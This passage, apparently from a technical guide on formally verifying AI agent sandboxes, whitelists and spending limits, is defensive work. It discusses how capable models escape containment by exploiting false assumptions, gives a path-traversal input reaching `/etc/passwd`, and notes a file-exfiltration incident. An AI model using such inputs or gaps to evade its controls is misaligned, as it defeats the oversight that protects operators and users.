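- Every memory access on the program's behalf stays within the program's own memory.
- Every file it uses is inside its assigned folder.
- Every network connection uses an allowed protocol and goes to an address on a list that the program cannot change.

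An error in another runtime, Wasmer, shows why a proof helps. Wasmer's function for deleting a directory checked the requested path and converted it to a safe one, but then passed the original path to the operating system, so a program could delete directories outside its folder. Eight other functions in Wasmer applied the same check correctly. In WaVe, the system call that deletes a directory has a precondition that the path is inside the program's folder, similar to the condition "x in A" in the calculation for the invoice harness. The verifier rejects code that does not guarantee this precondition.

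WaVe's users must trust its verification tool, the 43-line security policy, and the 567 lines that describe what system calls do. Johnson and colleagues tested these descriptions with large numbers of automatically generated calls and found no errors. They also assume that each program runs in a single thread and that its folder contains no files with special effects on the system.

WaVe also assumes that nothing else uses the program's folder. Otherwise, a second program could replace a file with a link to somewhere else after WaVe checks the path but before the operating system uses it. The invoice harness creates a fresh folder for each program because new invoices may arrive in `/work/invoices` at any time.

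### How a capable model can still get out

A containment theorem has the form "if these assumptions hold, then no program causes an effect outside the allowed sets". If the theorem is proved correctly, a program can cause such an effect only when one of the assumptions is false, however capable the model that wrote it. Greater capability therefore helps a model escape only by making it better at finding false assumptions.

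This qualifies Moon and Varshney's claim that their guarantee does not depend on the model's capability. The claim is correct for effects that pass through the harness, but whether all effects pass through it may depend on how good the model is at finding a way around it. In the worst case, a single false assumption that some program could exploit removes the guarantee, because the havoc includes that program. In practice, the system may stay secure until a model can find such a program.

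seL4's history suggests that the assumptions are the weaker part. Its developers report no integrity defects in the verified code since they finished the integrity proofs. They have found defects in configurations without proofs, such as the multicore version. Even in verified configurations, they have found small defects in every class of code that the proofs leave out. They advise anyone worried about the proof to look at its assumptions instead, since these are "much more likely to cause problems".

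Current models can exploit such weaknesses. Marchand and colleagues at the UK AI Security Institute and the University of Oxford tested models on a 2026 benchmark of containers with planted weaknesses. Claude Opus 4.5, released in November 2025, escaped in 56% of attempts, and Claude Mythos Preview, announced in April 2026, escaped at least once on every task. Because the researchers planted the weaknesses, these results don't measure how common such weaknesses are. OpenAI paused training and evaluation of its most capable models in September 2026 after a research model gained limited internet access. That incident is part of the background to OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, published that November.

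A proof still helps, because it leaves fewer assumptions to check. With an ordinary container, the company must trust a large shared kernel and its own configuration of the container. With WaVe, it must still trust the kernel, but the model's program can reach the kernel only through the runtime's checked functions.

### Writing down the trusted base

Anyone who claims that a sandbox contains a program should list everything the claim depends on. The table lists these dependencies for the invoice agent, in the case where the company runs the model's programs on a Linux server with a compiler like vWasm and a runtime like WaVe.

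| What to write down | Invoice agent |
|---|---|
| Allowed files, processes and endpoints | Copies of invoices in a fresh folder; the program's own process; no endpoints |
| What enforces each limit | The compiler confines memory; the runtime checks file and network requests and offers no function that starts a process |
| What the proofs cover | Specific versions of the compiler and runtime, which must match the ones on the server |
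| What the proofs take as correct | The security policy, the descriptions of system calls, the processor model, the stage that writes machine code, the verification tools, Linux and the hardware |
| Conditions on the setup | Nothing else uses the folder; it contains only ordinary files; each program has one thread |
| Other routes to the outside | The harness's own tools; any tool server running under the harness's account; any place where a program could find the bank key |
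| Software that handles the program's output | The harness's parser and the program that staff use to view logs |
| Who can change any of this | Administrators, the software update system and anyone who can approve an exception |
| What the claim leaves out | Timing and other hidden channels; programs that never finish; harmful requests that the harness's rules permit |
| How the company checks each assumption | A named person, a test and a date for the next check |

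The software that handles the program's output is easy to overlook. If a log viewer running outside the sandbox has a bug, carefully chosen output could take control of it. One of OpenAI's security requirements covers software that could be compromised while processing model outputs, according to Campus Technology's *OpenAI Pumps Brakes on Frontier AI Training After Hugging Face Breach* (2026). OpenAI also removed potentially vulnerable shared services from its research environments and reduced standing privileges, which limits the other routes to the outside.

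Zhang's trusted base also includes the human operator who approves requests and any administrator with direct access to the database, who could alter the records.

A company can test the last row by having a capable model attack the sandbox. In October 2026, OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* reported that the company had used its strongest models to test its strengthened containment this way. Such a test can reveal a false assumption but cannot show that none remain.

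The company could shorten its list of assumptions most by removing the `run` tool and having ordinary code add up the invoices. The model would then produce only text, and the company would no longer have to rely on the WebAssembly compiler or runtime. It would still have to trust the harness's parser and tools, the operating system and the hardware.

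## Proving an action whitelist

An action whitelist is a list of the actions a harness may carry out. The theorem to prove is that every boundary event is on the list, whatever the model outputs. The first section proved this by hand for a three-line program, but a real harness has far more code and a state that changes from step to step. To handle this for PocketFlow, a small open-source agent framework, Moon and Varshney first prove the property for a simple abstract machine. They then prove that the abstract machine can match every step the harness takes.

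### The model as a method with no body

In the Dafny code, the method that stands for the model has a declaration but no body:

```
method {:extern} GetActionFromLLM(c: Constants, v: Variables)
    returns (action: Action)
    requires v.WF(c)
```

The argument `c` holds the settings that stay fixed during a run, such as the workspace folder and the list of tools, and `v` holds everything that changes. The `requires` line allows the harness to call the method only when the harness's own state is well formed. The method has no `ensures` line constraining its result, so the call is a havoc over the type `Action`. In Dafny, the `extern` mark means that outside code will supply the value when the software runs.

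In the PocketFlow proof, the `Action` type has four variants. It fixes the form of each action but can still represent forbidden ones, such as a read outside the workspace or a call to an unlisted tool. As the first section explained, a narrower type would move the check into the parser, which Dafny does not verify. Keeping forbidden values in the type lets verified code reject them, which leaves less unverified code to trust.

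### Steps, events and the policy

The proof describes the harness as a *labelled transition system*. This has a set of states, a set of actions, a set of boundary events, an initial state, and a relation that says which steps are possible. In the step

```
s --a/e--> s'
```

the harness is in state s, receives action a from the model, emits event e and moves to state s′. If the invoice agent's model requests `/etc/passwd`, then a is that request and e is an event with no effect.

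The description of the harness must define at least one step for every state and action. Otherwise, it could satisfy any policy by defining no step for a forbidden action, even though the real software would still have to do something.

A policy Π(s, a, e, s′) is true or false of each step. For two of the invoice agent's rules, it would be:

```
Π(s, a, e, s') =
    (if e = read(path)         then path is inside /work/invoices)
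and (if e = pay(payee, amount) then payee is on the approved list)
```

This policy depends only on e, but using the other arguments allows stronger rules. For example, the company could add "e either has no effect or carries out exactly a". That would rule out a harness that receives a request to pay Harlow Paper but pays a different approved supplier.

### The three refinement conditions

Let M be the abstract machine and I the harness. Both receive the same actions, and each has its own states, events and policy. A relation R links abstract states to harness states, and a relation Q does the same for events. For the invoice agent, an abstract state might just be a list of past reads and payments. The harness's state also contains the conversation, the settings and any partly processed reply, and R would hold only if the two records of reads and payments agree.

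The harness refines the abstract machine if three conditions hold:

1. **Start.** R links the two initial states.
2. **Step.** Suppose R links s(M) to s(I), and the harness can take a step from s(I) on action a, emitting e(I). Then the abstract machine can take a step from s(M) on the same action a, emitting some e(M). Q links the two events, and R links the two new states.
3. **Policy.** For every matched pair of steps, if the abstract step satisfies the abstract policy, the harness's step satisfies the harness's policy.

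The abstract machine has to match the step using the same action, so it cannot replace a hostile request with a harmless one. The third condition guards against a careless choice of Q. For example, if Q linked the abstract event "no effect" to a real payment to Mallory Ltd, the condition would fail because the abstract step would satisfy its policy but the payment would not.

### The theorem and its proof

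The soundness theorem has two assumptions. Every step of the abstract machine must satisfy the abstract policy, for every sequence of actions, and the harness must refine the abstract machine. Every step of the harness then satisfies the harness's policy, whatever model chooses the actions.

For the proof, let a₀, a₁, a₂ and so on be the actions in an arbitrary run of the harness with an arbitrary model.

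- By the start condition, R links the initial states.
- Suppose R links the two states after i steps. The harness now takes a step on aᵢ. The step condition supplies an abstract step on aᵢ, after which R links the new states.
- By induction, the abstract machine has a run that matches the whole of the harness's run and uses exactly the same actions.
- The first assumption covers every sequence of actions, including this one, so each step of the abstract run satisfies the abstract policy.
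- By the policy condition, each step of the harness's run satisfies the harness's policy.

The model enters the proof only as the source of the actions, and the proof never uses any fact about them.

Dafny checks the first assumption with an invariant, as the hand proof does, using one lemma for the initial state and another for a single step. The step condition takes more work because it concerns the harness's full state. For PocketFlow, it needs an extra invariant, which states, among other things, that the step count stays within its limit and matches the length of the recorded history.

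### The PocketFlow proof

PocketFlow represents an agent as a graph. Each node does some work and emits a label, and the framework follows the edge with that label to the next node. Moon and Varshney verified the loop that does this, with a policy of three rules:

- The harness reads only paths under the workspace folder.
- It calls only tools on the list.
- It takes steps only until it reaches a fixed limit.

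A pipeline of language models wrote the formal material. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the source code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the abstract machine, the description of the harness, the relations and the proofs. Moon and Varshney ran the pipeline four times on two workflows, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to help answer questions. Dafny accepted every final proof, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds for each path through the graph. Each run used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens.

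These figures suggest that such proofs are practical, at least for a small framework. PocketFlow's developer advertises it as 100 lines long, and the proof covers only four kinds of action. A framework with dozens of kinds would need a proof with more cases, and Moon and Varshney leave larger frameworks such as LangChain to future work.

After verification, the full trusted base consists of:

- the harness's policy, which must express what the company wants;
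- the relations R and Q, which give the abstract states and events their meaning;
- complete mediation, the condition that the sandbox section examined;
- the parser and the small piece of code that passes its result to the harness;
- the Dafny verifier, and the compiler that turns verified Dafny into Python.

The proof covers every `Action` value, so the theorem holds even if the parser misreads a request to pay Harlow Paper as a request to pay Mallory Ltd. The parser only has to produce a value of the right type and cause no effects of its own. It would break the guarantee if it executed part of the model's text as code.

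Compiling the harness from verified source avoids translating it by hand, a step where errors are common. The alternative is to prove properties of a separate model of the code. *Stop Means Stop* (2026) does this for a small Rust gate that decides whether an agent's effects may go ahead. The abstract model follows the Rust code line by line, and tests compare the behaviour of the two. The verification found two defects that earlier testing had missed.

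### Proofs that establish nothing

Dafny checks the proofs, so the language models that wrote them are not part of the trusted base. But a language model can still write a correct proof of a useless theorem. For example, the theorem may be *vacuous*, meaning that it is true only because it has nothing to apply to. A verifier will accept a proof that "every payment went to an approved payee" for a harness that cannot make payments.

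The pipeline has two defences against this. One is an information barrier: the step that writes the safety property does not see the harness's code, so it cannot simply describe what the code already does. The other is a set of three gates that every specification must pass before the final verification:

1. **Resolution.** The Dafny files must parse and type-check within 30 seconds.
2. **Vacuity.** The pipeline strips the invariant down to the requirement that the state is well formed, and empties the bodies of the lemmas. Verification must now fail. If it succeeds, the specification was demanding almost nothing.
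3. **Discrimination.** A language model inserts a plausible mistake into the proof file. Verification must fail again, or the specification cannot tell a faithful description of the harness from a faulty one.

Moon and Varshney found a vacuous policy that passed all three. In the document workflow, the sensitive effect is reading a document. The code records each document read in a list named `docs_read` and checks it against `allowed_docs`. The pipeline's template for safety properties lacked these fields and instead had `tool_calls` and `allowed_tools`, which suited the other workflow.

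With the barrier in place, the pipeline used `tool_calls` to stand for the documents read, so the theorem was a real claim about documents despite the misleading name. To test the barrier's effect, Moon and Varshney also ran the pipeline without it. The language model then detected that the workflow had no list of allowed tools and wrote a specification in which `tool_calls` never changes. The theorem still required every entry in `tool_calls` to be an allowed tool, but `tool_calls` was always empty, so the theorem held no matter which documents the agent read.

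The gates missed this because they damage the part of the proof that covers how the loop works in general, which was sound and demanding in both versions. No gate tested whether each rule in the policy ever had anything to apply to. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that every list a rule mentions is non-empty in some reachable state.

Someone judging a whitelist proof can apply the same idea by hand. For each rule, they can ask for one run in which the harness performs a permitted action that the rule covers. For the invoice agent, this could be a $100 payment to Harlow Paper that appears in the list the theorem is about. They can then delete the harness's check and rerun the verifier. If the proof still succeeds, it never depended on the check.

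### Rules about arguments

A list of tool names is too coarse for the invoice agent, because the list has to include `pay`. The harness must also check the arguments. A developer could write these checks in a language such as Cedar, which is designed for rules about who may do what (Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues, *Cedar*, 2024). Amazon Web Services (AWS) developed Cedar and now applies it to agents, using a gateway between the agent and its tools that evaluates each tool call against the customer's Cedar policies. This service became generally available in March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026).

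Each Cedar policy either permits or forbids some requests. Cedar allows a request exactly when at least one `permit` policy matches it and no `forbid` policy does. It therefore denies by default, and a tool that no policy mentions stays unavailable. In slightly simplified form, a rule for the invoice agent could be:

```
permit (principal, action == Action::"pay", resource)
when {
    principal.getTag("department") == "accounts" &&
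    ["Harlow Paper", "Dunn Freight"].contains(context.input.payee) &&
    context.input.amount <= 1000
};
```

The conditions use data from two sources. The department comes from a login token, which the model can't alter. The payee and the amount come from the model's tool call, so a worst-case model can set them to anything. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* draws this distinction and recommends treating the model as an untrusted actor.

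Testing data from the model is safe when the tool will use the same data. If the model writes "Harlow Paper" to pass the test, Harlow Paper gets the money. Testing is unsafe when the data is a claim about something else. Suppose `pay` had a third argument, `approved`, and the policy required it to be true. A worst-case model would always set it to true, so the rule would restrict nothing.

In *LEANGUARD*, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026) avoid this problem with a harness check written in Lean, a programming language and proof assistant. The check takes the facts it needs from the company's database and its own record of events, never from text returned by a tool, so the model cannot satisfy a rule by stating that a customer has agreed. They proved that the check allows a call only if the call satisfies a separately written definition of the policy. In tests on τ²-bench, a benchmark of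 simulated customer service, agents without the check carried out at least 33 calls that the policy forbade, while agents with it carried out none.

Cedar and LeanGuard handle errors differently, which matters for a worst-case proof. LeanGuard denies a call if any relevant part of the policy fails to evaluate, for example because data is missing. Cedar skips a policy that produces an error, according to its security documentation. This is harmless for a `permit` policy, since skipping it can only lead to a denial, but an error in a `forbid` policy removes a prohibition.

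Suppose the company has one policy that permits all payments and another that forbids those whose `country` argument is on a sanctions list. If `country` is optional and the model leaves it out, the `forbid` policy fails with an error and the payment goes through. Cedar's validator catches this mistake if the company gives it a description of the tool's arguments. A whitelist made of narrow `permit` policies is safer still, because an error can only reduce what the agent may do.

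### Checking a policy automatically

Cedar has no loops, and evaluating a policy changes nothing. This lets a tool translate a set of policies into a logical formula P(r), which is true when the policies allow request r. An *SMT solver*, a program that either finds values that make a formula true or proves that none exist, can then answer questions about every possible request:

| Question | What the solver searches for |
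|---|---|
| Do the policies allow nothing? | A request r with P(r) true; finding none means yes |
| Do they allow everything? | A request r with P(r) false; finding none means yes |
| Does a new version P′ allow more than P? | A request r with P′(r) true and P(r) false |

Cutler and colleagues designed the translation to be sound and complete, so the answers are correct for the policies as written. The translation also uses only a part of logic in which a solver can always reach an answer. On their example applications, translating and solving took 75.1 milliseconds on average.

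AWS gives examples of the mistakes this catches. One policy requires a customer's tier to be both Gold and Platinum, so it allows no refunds. Another allows a discount if the order is for at least 100 items or for fewer than 100, which covers every order. Two other policies look reasonable separately, but one permits Gold customers to get refunds under $100 and the other forbids refunds under $500 to Gold and Platinum customers, so the first never takes effect.

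The last example is a policy change. The old version refuses discounts on limited-edition products, and the new one refuses them only for orders of more than 200. The edit loosens the policy, although the added condition makes it look stricter. An order for 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount.

These checks find policies that allow everything or nothing, but they cannot find a wrong number, such as a payment cap of $10,000 where the company meant $1,000. This mistake is a real possibility because AWS also offers to have a language model draft Cedar policies from plain English. Someone who knows what the company intended still has to read the policy.

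The settings need checking too. By default, the service refuses to create a policy when the analysis finds a problem, but AWS's *CreatePolicy* documents an option to ignore all findings. It also documents a log-only mode for collecting data on a policy's effects before making it active, and a policy left in that mode doesn't support any claim about what the agent can do.

The gateway also hides tools that the policies would always deny. AWS argues that a model cannot try to use a tool it does not know exists. A worst-case model can output any tool name, including one it has never seen, so a proof has to rely on the check made when the tool is called.

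Cedar evaluates a policy against one request at a time, so the policy can cap each payment at $1,000 but cannot keep the total under $5,000. The next section covers limits on totals, which require a record of earlier payments.

### Skills that contain their own code

Some agents load *skills*, which are packages of written instructions and scripts. Skills complicate a whitelist because one permitted call can start a script that does many other things. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) proposes three layers of checking. Each skill has a manifest that declares a set D of capabilities, such as reading a certain folder or contacting a certain host, and the checks are meant to show that nothing outside D happens.

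| Layer | Method | What it is sound for | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Analyse the scripts without running them | Every effect of every script | The model's own tool calls |
| 2 | Give the function that carries out tool calls a type that accepts only capabilities in D | Every tool call that reaches the system | What a script does once a permitted call has started it |
| 3 | Search all sessions up to a fixed length for an effect with no matching log entry | Sessions up to that length | Longer sessions |

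The first layer computes a set that includes every effect the script can produce, and possibly some it cannot. When the analysis cannot follow the code, for example because the script builds and executes new code, it assumes any effect is possible, so the skill fails.

In Metere's example, a skill's manifest declares that the skill fetches pages from one domain and reads a cache folder. The analysis finds that the skill's script also writes to that folder. The operator can then either declare the write in the manifest or change the script.

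The third layer works for up to about 100 tool calls. The system holds roughly that many before it compares its log with what actually happened, and that comparison covers longer sessions.

Metere combines the layers in a theorem that a skill which passes all three stays within D. The definition behind this theorem is too strict for a worst-case model, because it covers every capability that appears in a session, even in requests that the system refused. The property therefore fails for the same reason as "the model never asks to pay Mallory Ltd". Metere's argument does support the weaker claim that no effect outside D takes place, which is what an operator needs.

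The software that Metere released also does less than the theorems assume. Its first layer scans scripts for text patterns, which can miss effects written in a form nobody anticipated. The third layer tries every sequence of calls instead of using a solver. Metere gives 10 capabilities and 8 calls as a practical size, which already means about 214 million sequences. Three capabilities and 100 calls would mean about 10⁶⁰. An operator who wants the full guarantee would have to replace these layers with the stronger tools Metere describes, such as a proper program analyser and an SMT solver.

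### When the theorem is true but misses its purpose

A whitelist theorem can be correct and non-vacuous and still fail to prevent the harm the company had in mind. The clearest case is a list that includes a general shell, a tool that runs any command the model writes. The PocketFlow rule "the harness calls only tools on the list" then holds for every command, because the tool is always the shell, so the theorem rules out nothing that a command can do. Moon and Varshney warn that a shell reduces the guarantee to the shell's own limits. The invoice agent's `run` tool is of this kind, so its safety depends on the sandbox.

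LeanGuard stops any call whose effect it cannot determine. When Sankar and colleagues tested it on simulated attacks against agents, 13% of the calls it stopped were to tools whose effects it could not determine, including general shell commands.

In Moon and Varshney's Dafny code, the workspace rule requires the text of each path the harness reads to start with the name of the workspace folder. The path `/work/invoices/../../etc/passwd` passes such a test, but on most systems it leads to `/etc/passwd`, because each `..` means "go up one folder". A path inside the folder may also be a link to a file elsewhere. The theorem therefore limits which files the agent reads only if other code resolves the path first. Cedar's documentation likewise tells developers to put input into a standard form before asking for a decision.

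A listed tool can also change after someone has approved it. *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* (Kim and Kang, 2026) describes how an update can change the software that carries out a tool call. The same call still passes every check on its name and arguments, but it now has a different effect.

Lists of network destinations have a similar weakness. In January 2026, security researchers showed that files could leave Anthropic's Claude Cowork through a domain on its list of permitted destinations (Willison, 2026, *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*). The rule "the agent contacts only listed domains" can hold throughout such an incident. The users cared about who could obtain their files, and a domain name does not determine that when many customers have accounts with the same service.

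### Proving a narrower property

The fix in each case is to state the property in terms of the effect that matters and to include everything that determines where that effect ends up.

| Broad property | What it leaves open | Narrower property |
|---|---|---|
| The harness calls only listed tools, including a shell | Any command | The harness calls only listed tools, each with a fixed and limited effect |
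| Every path starts with `/work/invoices` | Paths and links that lead elsewhere | Every file the harness opens, after it resolves the path, is inside the folder |
| The agent contacts only listed domains | Whose account receives the data | Every request goes to a listed domain and uses the user's own account |
| The harness calls only listed tools | Updates that change a tool's effect | The harness calls only listed tools, in versions that the company has reviewed |

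For the invoice agent, the first repair means replacing `run` with a tool such as `add_lines(invoice)`, which can only return the sum of an invoice's lines. The third requires the harness to supply the login details, because if the model can supply them, the harness may not be able to tell whose account a request will use. If the harness removes any login details from the model's request and attaches the user's own, it can guarantee the narrower property whatever the model outputs.

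The invoice agent's `pay` tool takes a payee and an amount, and the harness looks up the payee's bank account in the company's records. If the tool also let the model supply an account number, every payee named in the log could be approved while the money went to someone else.

A narrower property can also block legitimate work. Kim and Kang compared ways of handling six calls that were waiting for approval when the software behind a tool changed. After the change, three calls would still have kept their data private and three would have made it public. Requiring the exact old version blocked all six. Their own method, which compares the new version's effects with what each call was meant to do, completed the three safe calls and blocked the others. It depends on an analysis of the tool's source code that errs on the side of listing too many effects, and that analysis becomes part of the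 trusted base.

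## Proving a spending limit

To enforce the invoice agent's $5,000 limit, the harness has to keep a running total of its payments. The proof has to show that this total is never less than the amount that has left the account.

Start with one payment at a time. Let L be the limit and `spent` the total so far:

```
havoc amount;
if amount >= 0 and spent + amount <= L
    then pay(amount); spent := spent + amount
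    else skip
```

The desired result is "spent ≤ L". The assignment rule turns it into "spent + amount ≤ L", which the test guarantees. The `skip` branch needs only "spent ≤ L". So the precondition is "spent ≤ L" whatever amount the model chooses.

The test `amount >= 0` is needed because a worst-case model could request a payment of −$4,000. Without the test, if the bank ignored the request, `spent` would fall by $4,000 while no money came back, and the model could pay out another $4,000. The calculation would still work and the theorem would still be true of `spent`, but the theorem would no longer limit what leaves the bank account. A complete proof therefore needs a second invariant, that the money paid out never exceeds `spent`.

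### Reserving before acting

Real agents complicate this in two ways. One reply can contain several tool calls, which the harness may run at the same time. Some actions also have no known price in advance. For example, the company pays its model provider for every call, and the price depends on how long the reply turns out to be.

A *reservation* handles both. Before each action, the harness works out an upper bound r on the cost and sets that amount aside. The variable `reserved` holds the total set aside for actions still in progress. When an action finishes at an actual cost of c, the harness replaces the reservation with that cost:

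```
reserve(r):    if spent + reserved + r <= L
                   then reserved := reserved + r
                   else refuse the action
settle(r, c):  reserved := reserved - r;  spent := spent + c
```

The invariant is

spent + reserved ≤ L.

- It holds at the start, when both variables are zero.
- Reserving adds r to the left side, but only if the result is still at most L.
- Refusing an action changes nothing.
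- Settling changes the left side by c − r, which is never positive, provided the action cost no more than its reservation.

At any moment, finished actions have cost `spent` and unfinished ones have cost at most `reserved`, so total spending stays within the limit throughout the run, even if the harness stops halfway through. The model influences which actions the harness considers and how large r is, but the reservation step preserves the invariant for every nonnegative r. The proof doesn't depend on any fact about the model, but it does depend on one fact about the world, that no action costs more than its reservation.

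Many tools check the bill afterwards instead:

```
if spent < L then  c := do(x); spent := spent + c
```

To keep the total within L after an action, "spent + c ≤ L" must hold beforehand for every possible cost c, and the test does not guarantee this. With $4,900 spent, the harness would still carry out a $4,000 payment and end at $8,900. If no action can cost more than m, and actions run one at a time, the rule guarantees only that the total stays below L + m. The company could keep the total within L by lowering the threshold to L − m, but that amounts to reserving m for every action, however cheap.

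*Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) tested limits on the cost of model calls, using an agent stuck in a retry loop with a cap of 2 cents. Two tools that track dollars but check after each call exceeded the cap in all 30 runs, as did three frameworks that limit only the number of steps. Khan's own program, which reserves money before each call, never exceeded it. The model ran at a setting that makes its outputs almost identical from run to run, so the 30 runs provide little more evidence than one run per tool. Better evidence comes from another 160 runs of Khan's program, which had more varied outputs and also stayed within the cap.

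### Three payments at once

Suppose the model's reply contains three payments of $2,000, all to approved suppliers, and the harness handles them at the same time. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* gives this case, which AWS uses to warn developers about a rule that looks correct. One version of the $5,000 limit adds up completed payments and the other adds up requests, with the payment under consideration included in both totals.

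| Event | Total under the rule for completed payments | Total under the rule for requests |
|---|---|---|
| First request | $2,000, allowed | $2,000, allowed |
| Second request | $2,000, allowed | $4,000, allowed |
| Third request | $2,000, allowed | $6,000, refused |
| Money paid in the end | $6,000 | $4,000 |

No payment has completed when the harness considers the second and third requests, so a rule that counts only completed payments excludes the pending ones. It checks `spent` but not `reserved`. A test in which each payment completes before the next request would not reveal the error, but a proof has to cover every reply, including this one.

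Summing requests is safe only if the harness tests the total and updates it in one indivisible step. Otherwise, three copies of the checking code could each read a total of $0, approve a $2,000 request, and write back a total of $2,000. The harness would have paid $6,000 but recorded only $2,000. Database engineers call this a *lost update*.

Agents are especially prone to this error. *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies in Multi-Agent Large Language Model Systems* (Khan, 2026) points out that an agent may read shared data, spend seconds or minutes generating text, and only then write. Database theory assumes a much shorter gap. Khan reproduced a lost update in deer-flow, an agent application from ByteDance. Locking the shared data prevents such errors, but in Khan's tests it raised token use by a factor of up to 1.6 with one model and 2.3 with another. A spending limit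 avoids most of that overhead because the harness needs the lock only while it reserves the money. It can release the lock before the slow call begins, since the reservation already accounts for the money.

If the harness sends a payment and crashes before the bank confirms it, the restarted harness has no record of whether the payment went through. Releasing the reservation could break the limit, and sending the payment again could pay the supplier twice. Zhang's runtime saves the reservation and the intended action before it sends anything. After a crash, it marks the outcome as unknown and does not blindly repeat the call. To preserve the invariant, the $2,000 has to stay reserved until someone checks with the bank.

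### Writing the rule in Dogwood

AWS released *Dogwood* in 2026 for rules that depend on earlier calls. It extends Cedar with conditions over the recorded history of a session. In outline, and not in Dogwood's exact syntax, a rule for the invoice agent modelled on an example in AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* would be:

```
forbid pay when total > 5000,
    where total = sum of amount over every pay::request
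                  in this session during the last 24 hours
```

The sum includes the current request. In the full syntax, a variable marks each request's place in the history, so two payments of $2,000 count separately. Changing `request` to `response` would produce the faulty rule from the table. That rule is unreliable even without simultaneous calls, because AWS records a response shortly after the call completes, and a fast second payment can arrive before AWS records the first response.

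Under the request rule, the harness keeps an authorised request in the sum even if the tool then fails to make the payment. The failed payment uses up part of the limit but never causes spending to exceed it. A negative amount would lower the sum, so the company also needs an ordinary Cedar rule that forbids negative amounts.

The rule's guarantee is narrower than "at most $5,000 in one run", for reasons that AWS's *Temporal policies* sets out:

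- The history covers one session, and the caller chooses the session's ID. A new ID starts a new total, so AWS warns that such limits do not hold against a caller who controls the ID. In the invoice agent, the harness must set it and the model must have no way to change it.
- No condition can look back more than 24 hours. A run that lasts longer can exceed $5,000 in total.
- If an administrator adds or edits one of these rules while a session is open, the service ends the session, and the next one starts with an empty history. The harness must then end the run or carry the old total over.

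According to InfoQ, Dogwood also requires the service to store events, and the time to evaluate a rule can grow with the length of the log. The events must be authentic and their timestamps correct, so the event log becomes part of the trusted base. AWS offers the public interpreter for trying out the language, not for production.

The largest loss is the automatic analysis described in the whitelist section, which does not work on Dogwood's temporal conditions. If someone changes `request` to `response` in a spending rule, a person has to notice the change. AWS made Dogwood a separate language because of this limitation. Raman (2026), in *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell*, lists this kind of decidable policy comparison among the reasons NVIDIA's OpenShell project is adopting Cedar for its sandbox rules.

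To enforce a single total, the company may not need a policy language. The two procedures `reserve` and `settle` take a few lines of code, and a verifier such as Dafny can check the invariant directly. Dogwood is more useful when a company has many rules about sequences and wants to change them without changing the harness.

### How overruns happen in practice

*Token Budgets* also contains a catalogue of agents that spent more on model calls than their users intended. Khan started with agent projects on GitHub that had at least 1,000 stars, and kept the 21 that either offered a budget or token limit or had an issue whose title was about excessive cost. Khan searched their issue trackers for words such as "budget", "runaway" and "infinite loop", which produced 167 candidates, and retained 110.

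| Type of case | Number |
|---|---|
| Confirmed overrun, reported by a user | 63 |
| Gap that a maintainer acknowledged | 28 |
| Request for a budget feature | 14 |
| Borderline | 5 |

One user lost about $2,150, the largest loss. Another lost $235 in four days to a loop in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent.

A second person independently labelled the cases as fixed bugs, unfixed bugs, maintainers' statements or feature requests. The two raters agreed well, with a Cohen's kappa of 0.84 (kappa measures agreement beyond chance, and 1 is perfect). These labels do not exactly match the four types in the table, so the agreement supports the figure of 63 only indirectly. Khan also sorted the cases by cause. Retry loops were the largest group, with 27 of the 110 cases, but the raters' kappa for cause was only 0.44, and Khan calls this grouping exploratory.

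The catalogue cannot show how common overruns are. Khan acknowledges that it selects "on the dependent variable", meaning that projects were included partly because they had the problem under study. It also leaves out closed products and reports in other languages. As a check, Khan examined 20 projects chosen only by popularity and found similar candidates in 12 of them, though only one person labelled those. The evidence does support the claim that overruns recur across independently written frameworks.

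### The delegation experiment

In 11 of the 110 cases, the main cause was an agent handing work to several others. Khan reproduced the fault with three child agents that run at the same time and share one budget. Each child makes one call costing 23 units (a unit is a thousandth of a US cent), so the three calls cost 69 units. The methods that reserve budget set aside 31 units per call.

| Method | Budget | Children admitted | Total spent | Runs over budget |
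|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shared counter without a lock (Python) | 60 | 3 | 69 | 30 of 30 |
| Shared counter with a lock and reservations (Python) | 60 | 1 | 23 | 0 of 30 |
| Budget split between the children (Rust) | 60 | 0 | 0 | 0 of 30 |
| Budget split between the children (Rust) | 100 | 3 | 69 | 0 of 30 |
| Shared counter with a lock and reservations (Rust) | 60 | 1 | 1 | 0 of 30 |

The unlocked counter fails the same way the $2,000 payments did. Each child checks the budget before its call and records the cost afterwards, so all three pass the check before any of them records a cost.

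Some of the results are weaker evidence than others. With a budget of 100, even the unlocked counter would have stayed within the limit, so that row shows only that the split budget lets work proceed when there is enough money. The Rust program with a lock used a shorter prompt that cost 1 unit per call, so three calls could never have reached 60. Its row shows that the reservations admitted one child and refused two. As in the earlier test, the 30 runs were nearly identical, and Khan presents them as a demonstration of a mechanism, not as a statistical result.

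Splitting the budget of 60 units gave each child 20, less than the 31 it needed to reserve, so nothing ran. A shared budget would have paid for one call. Splitting is a simple way to preserve the invariant, but it can leave money unspent when the shares are too small to use.

### What ownership types add

The Rust programs with split budgets rely on *ownership types*, whose values a program can use at most once. In Khan's library, a budget is one of these values. Spending from it uses it up and returns a new budget holding the remainder. Splitting it uses it up and returns two budgets that add up to the original. A program that copies a budget, gives it to two children, or spends from it after splitting it does not compile. Khan translated the faulty counter into Rust in three ways, and the compiler rejected all of them.

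The types let the compiler catch an incorrect counter before anyone deploys it, by ruling out the mistakes that would count the same money twice. Without them, the proof needs someone to confirm that every part of the harness takes the lock and reserves money before spending it. The types do not make a correct counter any safer. For a single agent, a four-line Python counter with the same estimates matched Khan's library, with no overruns in 30 runs.

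That assurance covers only the source code. Khan leaves open whether the compiled program preserves these properties, and a third-party library that uses `unsafe` Rust could forge a budget. The budget library also works only within one process, so a company running its agents on several servers would need a shared service to track their total spending.

### What the limit on model costs assumes

For a payment, the harness knows the amount in advance and can reserve exactly that, plus any bank fee. For a call to the model, it has to estimate. Providers charge by the *token*, a piece of text that is often shorter than a word, with separate prices for input and output. Most interfaces let the caller cap the length of the output, so the reservation is

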